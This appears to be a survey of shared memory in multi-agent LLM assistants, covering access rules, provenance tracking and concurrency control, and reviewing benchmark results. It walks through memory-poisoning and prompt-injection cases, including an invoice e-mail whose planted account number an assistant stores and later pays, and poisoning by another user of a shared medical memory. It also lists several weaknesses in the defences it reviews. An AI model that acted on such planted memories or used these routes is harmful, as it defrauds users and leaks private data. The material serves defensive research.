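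Code can remove forbidden entries before or after the search ranks them. Suppose a search returns the five entries that best match Ben's question, and all five are Cara's private notes. If the filter runs after ranking, it removes all five and Ben gets nothing, even though he is allowed to read the sixth-best match. If the filter runs before ranking, that entry comes first. Both methods keep Cara's notes from the model, but the empty result from filtering afterwards may hint to Ben that hidden notes on the subject exist.

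### Permissions that change over time

Ana's company may give Ben a new agent one month and take it away the next. Collaborative Memory represents these permissions as two sets of links that can change at any time. One set connects users to the agents they may use, and the other connects agents to the resources they may use, such as a bank account or a database. The system also permanently records when each memory fragment was created, who contributed it, and which agents and resources were involved.

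Let A(u, t) be the agents that user u may use at time t, and R(a, t) the resources that agent a may use. For a fragment m, let A(m) and R(m) be the agents and resources that went into it. When agent a works for user u, it may receive the fragments

M(u, a, t) = {m : A(m) ⊆ A(u, t) and R(m) ⊆ R(a, t)}.

Suppose a payments agent reads the company's bank account for Ana and saves a fragment about a supplier's last payment. Ben is allowed to use both the payments agent and a mail agent that has no access to the bank. He can receive the fragment through the payments agent, because both conditions hold, but not through the mail agent, because the second condition fails. If the company later stops Ben from using the payments agent, the first condition fails at his next request, and nobody has to edit the fragment.

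The formula does not check who contributed a fragment, so it cannot by itself protect private notes. The design therefore has two memory tiers, a private one for each user and a shared one. Separate write policies control what enters each tier, and the policy for the shared tier might remove names or block some content. Read policies can then narrow the permitted fragments further, for example by keyword.

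The design can leak derived information. R(m) lists the resources an agent accessed while creating the fragment. If the payments agent later restates its old fragment without opening the bank account again, the new fragment may not list the account, and the mail agent could then read the new fragment. Li, Wang and colleagues criticise this kind of gap in the design, where a conclusion drawn from a private fragment does not inherit the fragment's restrictions.

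### A route that skipped the check

Margalit, Cohen-Inger and colleagues (2026), in *Governed Shared Memory for Multi-Agent LLM Systems*, tested their own memory service, MemClaw, which customers already use. An entry's scope can be a single agent, a group of agents or the whole customer organisation, and a search should return only entries whose scope includes the agent searching.

They set up four groups of six agents. The first agent in each group saved one secret for itself and one for its group, then all 24 agents searched for all eight secrets. Of the 192 searches, 28 should have found the secret and 164 should not. The service returned the secret in 72 of those 164 and missed it in 4 of the 28. The searches used a key valid for the whole organisation and named the group as a filter, so they show that the filter was unreliable, but not how much an agent with its own restricted key could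 have found.

A smaller test with restricted keys exposed a clearer fault. An agent that knew an entry's identifier could fetch the entry even if it belonged to another group. The service identified the agent but checked only that the agent and the entry belonged to the same organisation. After the company fixed this, all 36 forbidden fetches failed. The agent now gets a "not found" reply, so it cannot tell whether the entry exists.

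In another test, agents found facts shared within their own group in 117 of 120 searches, and agents from other groups found none of them in 80 searches. This is better than the first result, but it doesn't explain the 72 leaks. Margalit and colleagues had no rival system to compare with, and they worked within one organisation's account, so they didn't test whether one customer can read another's memory.

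### When a model decides what is private

Few people want to choose readers for every note their assistant saves. Microsoft's AIM has a language model label each memory as public or private, and ordinary code enforces the label. User u may read memory m if

m is public, or m is private and u owns it.

The search index applies this rule before ranking, so another user's private memories never become candidates. If memories are labeled correctly, this protection doesn't depend on the model that answers the question. But if the model labels Ana's medical appointment as public, any user's search can retrieve it.

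Johnson and colleagues built the MUMBench benchmark to test this, with 672 interactions by 93 simulated users in coding, customer support, education and travel. The share of memories correctly labelled private or public ranged from 89.5% with Llama 3.3 70B to 96.0% with GPT-5.4. The benchmark contains 150 private memories and 56 public ones, so a program that labelled everything private would be right about 73% of the time. The share of correct labels also doesn't distinguish between labelling a public memory private, which makes it less useful, and labelling a private memory public, which exposes it to every user.

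Some entries have no correct label because they combine public and private facts. In one of the benchmark's ambiguous cases, a customer asks whether the weather is delaying a package. The weather is public knowledge, but the package is private to the customer, so the two facts should go into separate entries.

With only two labels, Ana also cannot share the supplier's details with Ben alone. She must either keep them to herself or show them to the whole company. In the text of *AIM*, only a memory's creator may update or delete it, but the pseudocode checks only whether the user may read it, which would let anyone delete a public memory.

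Nobody ran a competing system on MUMBench. On LOCOMO, a benchmark of long conversations without access rules, a judge model scored AIM's answers to single-fact questions at 0.280 and those of Mem0, a widely used memory system, at 0.671. AIM's score comes from one run and Mem0's from an average of ten, but the gap is large. The evidence that AIM controls access is therefore much stronger than the evidence that it finds the right memory.

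### Labelling entries by who was present

In Liu's design, the people who may read a new entry, its audience, are those who were in the conversation when the assistant recorded it. The software identifies them from their e-mail addresses, chat accounts or phone numbers, and does not rely on a model to decide who should read the entry. The assistant's owner belongs to every audience.

Let V be the set of people present now. An entry may enter the model's context only if

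V ⊆ A for at least one of the entry's authorised audiences A.

If Ben's assistant recorded a note while Ben was talking to Ana, the note's audience is {Ana, Ben}. The assistant can use the note when the two talk again, but not if Cara has joined them. If the software cannot identify someone in the conversation, it lets the assistant use only public entries.

Ben can also approve an extra audience, such as {Ben, Cara}. The software checks each audience separately instead of merging them, so the note stays out of a conversation among all three because nobody has approved that combination.

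Liu tested two implementations on 10,000 synthetic histories. Recall@5 is the share of entries needed for an answer that are among the five the search selects.

| Method | Contexts with a forbidden entry | Recall@5 |
|---|---|---|
| Search with no permissions | 82% | 0.674 |
| Separate memory for each session | 0% | 0.740 |
| Rank, then filter the top 20 | 0% | 0.972 |
| Filter, then rank (Liu's design) | 0% | 0.972 |

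Permissions improved recall because notes about other people no longer competed for the five places. On one question, recall without permissions fell from 0.974 to 0.616 as the number of such notes rose from none to eight, while recall with Liu's design stayed at 0.974. Filtering after ranking did equally well here because eight notes could not fill 20 places, but a large company's memory might contain hundreds of such notes.

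The absence of forbidden entries follows from the rule itself. None appeared in the 200,000 contexts that the two implementations assembled, but a single program generated every history, and the software had correct information about who was present. In a real office, the software might match a phone number to the wrong person and then apply the rule to that person.

Hidden notes can also slightly change the order in which a search returns the visible ones, because text search gives more weight to rare words and Liu's index counts words across everyone's notes. An audience specifies who may read an entry but not why, so if Ben may read the supplier's bank details to pay an invoice, the rule also lets him read them for any other reason.

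### Summaries of entries with different readers

Suppose the shared memory contains two entries. Ana and Ben may read the first, which gives Ana's budget for a project as €10,000. Ben and Cara may read the second, which gives Cara's quote as €12,000. A model combines them into a new entry: "Cara's quote is €2,000 over budget." Its readers are

{Ana, Ben} ∩ {Ben, Cara} = {Ben}.

Ana knows the budget, so she could work out the quote from the summary, and Cara could work out the budget in the same way. Taking the union of the two lists would therefore reveal both figures to everyone on either list. FIDES and CaMeL also take the intersection for data inside a single task, but a memory has to store the resulting list for future sessions.

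If the two facts don't need to be in one sentence, the software can write a separate summary for each audience. If it has lost track of an entry's sources, under Liu's design it either doesn't create the summary or quarantines it. Suppressing every mixed summary would be simpler, but in a small comparison it left none of the eight derived entries available, while the intersection rule kept all eight available.

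Someone may also approve a wider audience for the finished summary. That approval covers only this summary, so a later summary built on it does not inherit the wider audience. If it did, that audience could still read the later summary after the approval had ended.

### Withdrawing permission

Suppose Ana withdraws Ben's permission to read her budget. Changing the first entry's readers to {Ana} stops the assistant from retrieving it for Ben. But if the software saved {Ben} as the summary's list of readers, he can still look up the summary. He knows Cara's quote, so he can subtract €2,000 from it to recover the budget.

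The software can prevent this by working out the summary's readers from its sources at every read:

readers(summary, t) = readers(budget, t) ∩ readers(quote, t).

After the withdrawal, the intersection is {Ana} ∩ {Ben, Cara} = ∅, so nobody may read the summary. The software could also mark every dependent entry as invalid and rebuild it. Similarly, when someone retracts an entry, MemTX follows the links to everything derived from it, revokes the conclusions, and withholds summaries, index entries and shared copies until it can rebuild them from the remaining sources. MemTX cannot find a copy that nobody linked to its source.

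In Liu's design, withdrawing an extra audience's access deletes one record, and deleting an entry deactivates everything derived from it. Removing a person takes that person off every list. These changes apply from the next model call and don't affect a call already under way. Liu describes these rules but doesn't test them.

An access list cannot control some copies of an entry. A colleague may have already loaded the shared workspace into a session, or someone may have received an e-mail that quoted the budget. Lin and colleagues note that restoring an earlier state of the memory can conflict with a later request to erase something. For example, an administrator who restores last week's backup after an attack might bring back an entry that Ana deleted yesterday. Lin and colleagues also describe MemT-1.0, which stores its memory as a matrix of numbers that every update modifies, so it has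 no separate entry with an access list that Ben could be removed from.

### How current systems score

*GateMem* (2026) tests whether assistants with many users can answer legitimate questions, protect restricted information and forget what users tell them to delete. It contains 91 long simulated histories from medical, office, education and household settings, with 2,218 test questions. A patient's relative, for example, may learn the time of an appointment but not a lab result. The assistant has information about who is asking and which rules apply.

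Let U be the share of legitimate questions that the assistant answers fully, A the share of restricted questions where it breaks the access rules, and F the share of questions about deleted information where it fails to forget. The overall score is

U × (1 − A) × (1 − F).

An assistant scores zero if it refuses everything or if it reveals every secret. The table shows results for GPT-5.4 with four kinds of memory.

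| Setting and memory | U | A | F | Score |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Medical, full history in the context | 91.4% | 10.4% | 2.3% | 80.1% |
| Medical, ordinary search | 64.8% | 25.0% | 7.9% | 44.7% |
| Medical, search with access information | 37.1% | 10.9% | 4.0% | 31.8% |
| Medical, Mem0 | 38.1% | 28.1% | 5.6% | 25.8% |
| Office, full history in the context | 89.6% | 33.9% | 4.5% | 56.5% |
| Office, ordinary search | 74.0% | 29.8% | 9.5% | 47.0% |
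| Office, search with access information | 76.0% | 19.9% | 6.3% | 57.0% |
| Office, Mem0 | 40.3% | 16.4% | 14.4% | 28.8% |

Access information reduced violations in both settings, but in the medical one it also left the assistant unable to answer many legitimate questions. The six models tested usually scored best with the full history, because it contained all the evidence they needed. It also contained every secret, and in the office setting GPT-5.4 broke the rules in a third of the restricted cases. DeepSeek-V4-Pro scored more evenly, between 67.9% and 71.0% in all four settings with the full history.

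A and F slightly overstate leakage because they also count replies of the wrong type that reveal nothing. For instance, if a user asks about deleted information, the assistant must reply that it has no such memory, and an ordinary refusal counts as a failure. The forgetting test checks only what the assistant reveals, not whether the deleted data is still on disk.

In tests on medical cases with the weaker GPT-4o-mini, the assistants often failed on indirect questions. In one such question, a relative asks whether a patient's chart is for dermatology or for a sexually transmitted infection. Two memory systems each named one of the two, but marked their replies as redacted.

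These scores provide little evidence about strict reader lists, because none of the seven methods tested keeps one. Even the search with access information is a light safeguard that relies partly on the model to follow the rules it receives. GateMem also couldn't score Liu's design fairly, because the benchmark has no authoritative list of who may read each piece of information.

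## Recording where a stored memory came from

An access list controls who may read a note, but Ana can be harmed by a note she is allowed to read. Suppose that in March her assistant reads the invoice e-mail with the thief's account number. Ana doesn't pay the invoice that day, so the assistant saves a summary in its memory: "Ana pays the paper supplier at account 55501234." In April, she types, "Pay the paper supplier's new bill." The assistant finds the note, treats it as Ana's own preference and pays the thief.

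The note contains no instruction, so a filter that looks for planted commands would not flag it. But the summary has dropped the fact that the number came from a stranger. The memory has gained authority that its source never had, which *SAFE-Mem* (Li, Kang and colleagues, 2026) calls authority laundering, a term it credits to Zhan and colleagues.

Xu, Xiao and colleagues (2026), in *Memory Provenance Laundering in LLM Agents*, measured how often this laundering happens. Six small and mid-sized models condensed attackers' text into memories, using a prompt that did not ask them to track sources. In scenarios based on AgentDojo, the models recorded outside content as the user's history, workflow or confirmation in 95.8% to 100% of the memories. Only 5% to 49% of the attacks then led to the harmful action, so an agent that rarely takes the harmful action may still store many laundered claims.

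### What memory-poisoning studies have found

Attackers need little access to plant a memory. In studies that Lin and colleagues survey, some attackers could write directly to the store, and one such attack succeeded more than 80% of the time after poisoning less than 0.1% of the entries. Others only asked the agent ordinary questions or changed a web page that the agent then visited. The planted memory can be a false fact or a procedure that the agent saves as a successful way to do a task and later repeats.

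Memories can also become inaccurate without an attacker. In one study, agents sometimes saved a user's claim in more confident words than the user had chosen. Removing bad memories is hard because agents build new memories from old ones. When researchers deleted harmful skills from an agent that learns from its own past work, the agent recovered little of its lost performance, but it recovered more when they also deleted everything derived from those skills.

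### Signed entries with a family tree

Ouyang and Hou (2026), in *Memlineage*, describe a system that records each memory entry's ancestry and checks it before sensitive actions. They assume an attacker who knows the whole design and controls web pages, documents, tool results or messages from other agents. They also assume the attacker cannot alter the program that runs the agent, steal its keys or change the model.

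When Ana's assistant saves its summary, MemLineage records the author, the time, a fingerprint of the source data and the summary's parents, which are the entries the model had in its context. It signs this record with the author's private key and adds the record's fingerprint to an append-only log. Any later edit to the entry invalidates the signature. But the assistant did write the summary, so the signature covering the thief's account number is valid, and the problem can be detected only from the list of parents.

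Each entry also has a level: 0 for trusted, 1 for derived from trusted entries, 2 for derived from untrusted ones, and 3 for external. A weight w(p, c) between 0 and 1 estimates how much parent p influenced entry c. The level of c is the highest level among the parents whose weight exceeds a threshold τ:

level(c) = max {level(p) : w(p, c) > τ}.

The simplest version gives every entry in the context a weight of 1, which works like the cautious join in FIDES. A second model can instead estimate the weights, so that an irrelevant e-mail in the context doesn't taint the summary.

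Those estimates can fall low enough to break the chain. Ouyang and Hou tested a scripted judge whose weights start at 0.9 and fall by 30% with each rewrite, giving 0.9, 0.63, 0.44, 0.31 and 0.22. With τ = 0.3, the fifth rewrite has no parent above the threshold. MemLineage labels such entries trusted by default, so the thief's number would become trusted after five rounds of summarising. Ouyang and Hou prove that an untrusted label survives if every weight along the path exceeds τ, but the proof does not guarantee that the judge's weights will exceed it.

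An entry with no recorded parents also counts as trusted by default. A stricter setting blocks sensitive actions based on such entries, but it would also block a payment based on a note Ana typed herself, unless she confirmed it again.

Before a payment, code looks up the memories that mention the account number. If any of them derives from an external source, the code can refuse the call, ask Ana, or replace the number with one from a trusted entry. The assistant can still use the note to answer questions.

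The main experiment runs three scripted attacks against a scripted agent. All three succeeded with no defence. Signatures alone stopped the one attack whose author had no registered key, and MemLineage stopped all three. This confirms that the code follows its rules, but it doesn't measure how well those rules work with a real model.

The tests with real models are small. In one, GPT-5.3-Codex summarised a malicious document in one session and recalled the summary in another. It made the harmful call in 5 of 20 trials with no defence and in none with MemLineage, though the confidence interval for the MemLineage rate reaches 16%. Ouyang and Hou also ran six pairs of tasks and attacks from AgentDojo's Banking suite, with an agent set up to trust instructions in tool results. All six attacks succeeded without MemLineage and none with it. The agent completed two of the six user tasks when MemLineage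 only refused calls, and four when it replaced the attacker's values with correct ones. Those correct values came from the benchmark's answers, and a real system would need its own trusted record of each bill.

### Matching a memory's rank to an action's risk

Xu and colleagues' Provenance-Preserving Memory Firewall (PPMF) avoids estimating influence. It is designed for an attacker who controls what the agent reads during an earlier task and may include false claims that the user has approved something. This attacker is assumed to be unable to write the provenance records, change an action's risk rating or press the real confirmation button.

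Ordinary code gives each memory a rank according to how the information arrived:

unknown < external < trusted tool < user history < user confirmed < system.

The model writes the memory's text but cannot set its rank. A claim based on several sources gets the lowest rank among them, unless the platform has recorded the user's approval for that particular target and kind of action. Each tool call has a minimum rank for the claims that support it.

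| Proposed action | Lowest rank that can support it |
|---|---|
| search or read | external |
| open a saved workflow | user history |
| send, post or delete | user confirmed |
| buy or pay | user confirmed |
| change a password | user confirmed |

In April, the assistant proposes a payment to account 55501234. Code finds the memories that contain this number and uses the lowest rank among them. The note came from an e-mail, so its rank is external, and PPMF refuses the payment until Ana confirms that account. Her earlier confirmation of a payment to another supplier doesn't count, because it was for a different account.

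Xu and colleagues turned 726 recorded AgentDojo runs into memory tests, of which 629 were attacks and 97 were legitimate actions that the user had confirmed. Without a defence, every attack succeeded. A filter for suspicious words let 51.8% of the attacks through and blocked 22.7% of the legitimate actions. PPMF stopped every attack and allowed every legitimate action. However, an attack counted as successful only if it caused a high-risk action that the user had not authorised, which is almost exactly what the gate blocks. A perfect score was therefore likely as long as the records were correct.

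PPMF also has to find the confirmation. With 20 distracting memories added to each case, it allowed only 79.4% of the legitimate actions when ten memories were retrieved, but 99.0% when 20 were retrieved.

Neither PPMF nor MemLineage protects Ana if she asks which account the paper supplier uses. Reading counts as low-risk, so the assistant may give her the thief's account number, and she may then send the payment herself.

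### Different authority for different uses

Hiding every memory that came from outside would close that gap, but the same e-mail may contain a delivery date that Ana needs. SAFE-Mem instead splits what it reads into separate claims and determines what each claim may be used for. Its threat model resembles the other two, but also includes an attacker who is another user of the same memory.

A model sorts each claim into one of five kinds, ordered by how much they bind the agent:

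description < attribute < preference < rule < permission.

A description only records what a source stated. An attribute is a fact about someone or something, a preference guides choices, a rule applies whenever its conditions are met, and a permission changes what the agent may do or whom it may trust.

Code separately sets the claim's authority, the strongest kind that its source can establish. Ana's own messages can establish anything about her, up to a permission. Another person in a conversation can establish attributes of themselves, while an e-mail or web page can establish only descriptions. The claim's effective level is

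level = min(kind, authority).

Suppose the model classes "Ana pays the paper supplier at account 55501234" as a rule. The claim's level is still description because it came from an e-mail. If Ana asks what was on the March invoice, the assistant may report the number. If she asks which account to pay, answering requires more than a description, so the claim doesn't enter the model's context, but her own note with the supplier's real account does.

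A model classifies each request by the kind of claim it needs. The model reads only the request, so planted text cannot influence it, but its classification can be wrong. Li and colleagues labelled 150 requests by hand to test this step. GPT-5.6-terra's labels for whether a description was enough matched theirs in 94.0% of cases, and GPT-4o-mini's matched in 85.3%.

The researchers put all 6,240 cases of MPBench, a memory-poisoning benchmark, into one user's memory. Attack success below is the share of 2,999 attacks in which the assistant's answer endorsed or acted on the planted memory. The user had asked the assistant to remember 249 things, and recall is the share of these that it later produced.

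| Defence | Attack success, GPT-5.6-terra | Attack success, GPT-4o-mini | Recall, GPT-5.6-terra | Recall, GPT-4o-mini |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 26.7% | 49.8% | 75.9% | 79.5% |
| MemLineage | 24.6% | 45.4% | 72.3% | 81.1% |
| TMA-NM, which withholds everything from outside | 2.7% | 2.4% | 9.6% | 9.6% |
| SAFE-Mem | 2.6% | 6.2% | 86.3% | 85.9% |

TMA-NM lost most of what users wanted to keep, because their requests to remember something usually came with outside content. MemLineage barely changed the answers, but it is designed to check actions, which this table doesn't cover.

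With GPT-4o-mini, SAFE-Mem stored the planted claim in 57.6% of attack cases but let it reach the model's context in only 2.8%. Li and colleagues also tested showing the model such claims with a marker limiting them to description, instead of withholding them. Attack success with GPT-4o-mini then rose from 6.2% to 19.6%, because the restriction depended on the model following the marker.

Withholding claims can also lower accuracy. On the LOCOMO conversations, SAFE-Mem with GPT-4o-mini answered 54.6% of questions correctly, compared with 58.4% when it withheld nothing. On another benchmark, its accuracy on questions about a user's preferences was half that of an ordinary memory, though there were only 30 such questions.

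In the test with a hostile fellow user, the attacker filled a shared medical memory with misleading examples so that questions about one patient would retrieve another patient's records. The agent wrote code for the wrong patient in 72.4% of cases, but SAFE-Mem blocked all of that code from running because the patient identifier came only from entries with another user's authority. Giving each user a separate memory also stopped the attack, but it removed 71.4% of the memories that harmless questions would have retrieved, compared with 2.0% for SAFE-Mem.

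### Carrying labels from one request to the next

CaMeL protects a plan by writing it before the agent reads any outside text. But if the planner can read results stored from earlier requests, an e-mail from Monday can influence Tuesday's plan. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) extends CaMeL's method across requests.

Suppose that Ana asks her assistant on Monday to find an invoice and keep its details, and on Tuesday to pay it. SPA stores the details, their label and a short description separately. Monday's planner wrote the description before any tool ran, so it contains nothing from the e-mail. Tuesday's planner sees only the description and the data's format, and writes a plan that retrieves the stored value by reference. The value comes back with its old label:

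ℓ(x) = ℓ_stored ⊔ ℓ_pc,

where ℓ_pc is the program counter's label at that step. Code checks the whole plan before running any of it. If the payment tool requires trusted arguments, SPA rejects the plan, whether the invoice is forged or genuine. It doesn't ask the planner for another attempt, so a planner cannot use rejections within a request to extract information, as it could with CaMeL.

Girrens and Wang tested SPA with GPT-5.4-nano on AgentDojo. They also split AgentDojo's 97 tasks into sequences of two to five requests, a version they call AgentDojo-MQ.

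| Setting | Utility, one request | Attack success, one request | Utility, several requests | Attack success, several requests |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Flow control off | 53.0% | 0.4% | 62.5% | 0.3% |
| Flow control on | 29.0% | 0.0% | 35.3% | 0.2% |
| Flow control off, planner sees stored values | not tested | not tested | 65.9% | 0.6% |

On single requests, attack success was at most 0.4% in every configuration, including two that hide the installed tools from the planner, as ACE does. Fixing the plan in advance therefore left few attacks for flow control to stop. Turning on flow control stopped the last four successful attacks out of 949 but cut utility from 53.0% to 29.0%. This drop in utility is a severe case of label creep, since many ordinary tasks use outside data in an action.

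The agent still reused its earlier work when labels were stored. With flow control on, later plans retrieved an earlier result in 89.9% of cases where one was available, compared with 95.4% when it was off. The 0.2% attack success rate on several requests comes from two runs that AgentDojo counted as successes even though SPA had rejected their plans.

These tests barely measure delayed attacks, because only 0.6% of attacks succeeded even when the planner could read everything in storage. Girrens and Wang acknowledge that AgentDojo's attack, which targets the current task, is a weak test of poisoning that takes effect later.

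### Relevance and admissibility

A memory search ranks entries by how well they match a question, and the thief's note matches Ana's request about the supplier very well. *MAP-Graph* (Wang, Yan and colleagues, 2026) separates this relevance from admissibility, which is whether a given agent may use an entry for a given action.

MAP-Graph first removes entries that the agent has no permission to read. It then scores each remaining entry m for a question q and an agent a:

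score = s(m, q) × ρ(m, a),

where s measures similarity and ρ measures trust in the entry's ancestry. An untrusted ancestor multiplies ρ by 0.25 and a private one by 0.45, so an entry with both keeps about 11% of its trust. If the other factors are equal to 1, the thief's note with a similarity of 0.9 scores 0.225 and ranks below a clean note with a similarity of 0.3.

Ranking alone isn't enough, because the thief's note may be the only one on the subject. MAP-Graph checks again once it knows the proposed action. It requires a trust score of at least 0.30 for an answer and 0.85 for a high-risk action, and any untrusted ancestor blocks a high-risk action regardless of its score.

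On 2,700 synthetic tasks for teams of four agents, MAP-Graph allowed a forbidden action in 1.5% of cases, compared with 20.8% for the best of seven alternatives. Its reported success rate of 95.0% is generous, because any safe refusal counted as a success when the action should not have been allowed. It chose exactly the right response in 72.7% of cases.

Wang and colleagues then switched off one part at a time. Without the final check on actions, forbidden actions rose to 27.0%. Without the permission filter, the share of exactly correct responses rose to 78.6%, but every observed attempt to read a forbidden entry succeeded. This version would have looked like an improvement in a test that measured only the agents' final decisions. They cleared the memory between tasks, so they did not test whether the system would catch a note retrieved weeks later.

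### Errors in the first label

All these systems pass labels on faithfully, even when the original label is wrong. If a developer marks Ana's mail tool as a trusted source, the thief's number is labeled trusted, and so is every summary that draws on it.

Xu and colleagues tested PPMF with corrupted records. When 20% of the source labels were missing, no attack succeeded, because PPMF treats a missing source as unknown. However, the share of legitimate actions it allowed fell to 81.4%. Changing 10% of the sources to "user history" also let no attack through, because high-risk actions need a confirmation. Forging 10% of the confirmations let 8.8% of attacks succeed, and lowering the risk rating of 10% of the actions to "read" let 11.2% succeed.

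Pasted text is a more everyday problem. SPA trusts the user's request and MemLineage trusts user prompts, so if Ana copies the invoice into her message, the thief's number may be trusted as if it came from her. SAFE-Mem can treat a pasted page as outside content, but only if the interface records it separately from the words she typed. Even then, if she writes "Remember the payment details in this invoice," SAFE-Mem treats this as an endorsement and raises the claims she refers to, but no higher than the kind she asked for. In the MPBench test with GPT-5.6-terra, 103 of the 370 claims it raised came from requests that referred to a document in this way.

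Signatures also require protecting the signing keys. In MemLineage, the program that runs the agent may hold the private keys of both the agent and the user. An attacker who takes over that program can sign false entries in Ana's name, and the log will preserve them as genuine. Ouyang and Hou exclude this attack from their threat model. The list that matches authors to public keys needs protection too. After an early mistake in development, Ouyang and Hou made their software refuse a second registration under an existing name, because an attacker could otherwise replace an author's key.

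Even with correct labels and safe keys, a record of origin does not show that a claim is true. If a fraudster posing as the supplier phones Ana and persuades her to type in a new account number, the entry has her signature, her full authority and no untrusted parents. Li and colleagues say that SAFE-Mem does not cover such errors, and suggest combining it with defences that examine a memory's content.

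## Coordinating simultaneous reads and writes

A note from a trusted source can be true when an agent reads it but out of date by the time the agent acts on it. Suppose Ana and Ben each have an assistant, and both assistants pay suppliers from a team budget of €1,000 recorded in the shared memory.

| Time | Ana's assistant | Ben's assistant | Budget on record |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10:00 | reads that €1,000 is left | | €1,000 |
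| 10:01 | | reads that €1,000 is left | €1,000 |
| 10:03 | pays €700, records €300 left | | €300 |
| 10:04 | | pays €700, records €300 left | €300 |

The team has spent €1,400, but the record shows €300 left, and both assistants report that they stayed within the budget. No attacker was involved, both users are authorized to spend the money, and a rule that compares each payment with the €1,000 balance the assistant read would allow both payments.

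### Transactions, locks and compensation

Databases prevent this with transactions, which are groups of reads and writes that take effect together or not at all. Isolation determines when other transactions can see those effects. Serializability, a strong form of isolation, requires the same result as running the transactions one after another in some order. If either assistant had finished before the other started, the second would have read €300 and stopped. Neither order produces two payments, so the timeline above is not serializable.

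One remedy is two-phase locking, in which a transaction takes a shared lock on whatever it reads and an exclusive lock on whatever it writes, and holds them until it finishes. Both assistants can hold a shared lock on the budget, but then neither can get the exclusive lock it needs to record a payment. This is a deadlock, and the database has to cancel one of the transactions.

Optimistic checking lets both continue. Each transaction notes the version of every item it reads and keeps its writes private until it commits, which makes them permanent. It may commit only if

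version now(k) = version read(k) for every item k that it read.

If both assistants read version 7 of the budget and Ana's commits first, that commit creates version 8. Ben's assistant still has version 7, so its commit fails and it starts again from €300.

Once an effect has reached the outside world, only a compensating action can reverse it. For a payment, that would be a refund, if the supplier agrees.

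### Why agents are harder to coordinate

According to *Position* (2026), a paper calling for more work on this problem, database transactions finish in microseconds, whereas a model takes seconds to minutes. A lock held that long blocks everyone else who needs the same data. Optimistic concurrency control avoids the lock by checking for conflicts only at the end, but a failed check can waste minutes of paid computation.

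Agents also read far more than they need. *CoAgent* (Lyu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) points out that agents search whole code repositories and list every service on a cluster of servers, so their reads often overlap with somebody else's writes. Many of their actions also take effect immediately. An agent repairing a live server has to see what each change does before choosing the next, so it cannot keep its changes private until it finishes.

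### Reads hidden in the context

An optimistic check requires a record of what each agent read. A database can record every query, but it can't record when an agent reuses a figure from earlier in its context without calling a tool again.

*S-Bus* (Khan, 2026) describes a server for agents that share text entries. The server logs the name and version of each entry an agent fetches, so agents don't have to declare what they read. When an agent commits a change, the server rejects it if any other entry in that agent's log has changed since it was fetched.

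Khan measured how many reads such a log can miss, using GPT-4o-mini agents on tasks modelled on the coding benchmark SWE-bench. Of 128,622 reads, 95,022 (74%) did not appear in the agents' tool calls, and the share ranged from 51% to 84% depending on the kind of task. The software counted a hidden read whenever an agent's output named an entry that the agent had not fetched in that step, so some of these reads may be mentions that did not influence the work.

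Many of these hidden reads are still in the log from an earlier step. If Ben's assistant fetches the budget at step 5 and relies on it at step 12, the log still holds the version from step 5, so the server can detect that the budget has changed. Over a whole session, the log contained 99.8% of the entries that agents said they had used. Agents overstated their use, by 32% according to a model judge and 49% according to a person. This doesn't imply that true coverage is below 70%, as Khan concludes, because the log contained nearly every entry the agents named, whether or not they had used it. It is still unknown how much they used without naming it. The log also omits anything an agent learned from another system.

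In another test, four agents designed a data pipeline together. Each wrote one part and read all four. Without the check, 590 of 639 commits relied on an outdated entry, compared with none of 638 with the check. The check rejected about one attempt for each successful commit.

Up-to-date reads don't guarantee a coherent result. When all the agents wrote to the same entry, S-Bus preserved every agent's contribution, but the final text contradicted itself in every trial, compared with 85.6% of trials without the check. Khan recommends S-Bus only where each agent writes to its own entry.

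### Letting a model judge the conflict

CoAgent avoids restarting an agent whenever something it read has changed. It ranks the agents before they start and aims for the result they would have produced by working one at a time in that order. An agent's reads include changes by agents ranked before it but not by those ranked after it.

If an earlier-ranked agent changes something that a later-ranked agent has already read, CoAgent adds a notice to the later agent's context. That agent's model decides whether the change affects its plan, and may ignore the notice or redo only the actions that relied on the old value. Changes by later-ranked agents never send notices to earlier-ranked ones, because two agents could otherwise keep correcting their work in response to each other forever.

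Writes can also arrive in the wrong order. If an earlier-ranked agent changes an object after a later-ranked one has, ordinary code undoes the later agent's write where necessary and restores the right order, without calling a model. To allow this, each tool that changes something first saves what it will need to reverse the change. For example, a tool that deletes a database first saves a copy.

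A payment or an e-mail can't be reversed this way, so CoAgent delays it until every earlier-ranked agent has committed. If Ana's assistant ranks first, Ben's payment has to wait, and his assistant receives a notice that only €300 is left. CoAgent has no budget rule of its own, so if the model wrongly dismisses the notice, Ben's payment still goes through.

Lyu and colleagues demonstrate the method on a cluster where a faulty update left several services running the wrong software. One agent repairs the services while another makes a trial copy of one of them, with the software that service currently runs. Without coordination, the repairing agent lists the services to repair before the copy exists, and the copying agent copies the faulty software before it is repaired. Both agents report success, but the copy stays faulty. Giving each agent its own objects to write would not have prevented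 this, because the two never wrote to the same object.

| Method | Time | Final state |
|---|---|---|
| One agent after the other | 50.2 s | correct |
| No coordination | 31.8 s | faulty copy |
| Locking | 53.1 s | correct |
| Optimistic checking | 63.7 s | correct |
| CoAgent | 32.8 s | correct |

Lyu and colleagues ran each method 100 times on ten pairs of tasks from two benchmarks, one for office work and one for server repair, using the inexpensive model DeepSeek v4 flash. They wrote the second task in each pair to conflict with the first. Uncoordinated agents reached a correct result in 13% of runs. Compared with running one agent at a time, CoAgent was 1.4 times as fast and used 1.15 times as many tokens. Its correctness was about 5% lower, because the model misjudged a notice in five runs. Locking was only 1.04 times as fast as running one agent at a time, and it averaged 0.81 deadlocks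 per run. Optimistic checking was slower than running one agent at a time and used 1.83 times as many tokens.

Conventional methods may add less overhead where conflicts are rarer. Khan (2026) found in *Verified Detection and Prevention of Concurrency Anomalies* that snapshot isolation, in which each transaction reads the data as it was when the transaction began, added about 8% to token use on one workload. Locking used 1.6 to 2.3 times as many tokens.

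CoAgent also needs every tool to declare what it reads and writes, which a general command line cannot do. A second model therefore builds tools on request and writes their declarations. On 71 server tasks, an agent with these tools solved 63 and took 80% as long as an agent with a plain command line, which solved 45. That test had no competing agents. A wrong declaration could also make CoAgent miss a conflict.

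### One check over the whole task

Chen, Dong and colleagues (2026), in *Cordon*, take the opposite approach to outside effects and hold them all back until the end. Cordon runs a task in three stages:

1. **Prepare.** The agent works on a separate copy of its files. Messages and other outside actions go into an outbox, and the software records which results each change or message derives from.
2. **Validate.** Code checks all the changes, pending actions, permissions and lineage together.
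3. **Commit or abort.** If the check passes, Cordon applies the file changes and releases the outbox. Otherwise, it discards both.

Cordon's commit rule is

commit(T) ⇒ valid(T, C_t) ∧ staged(E) ∧ recoverable(W, D).

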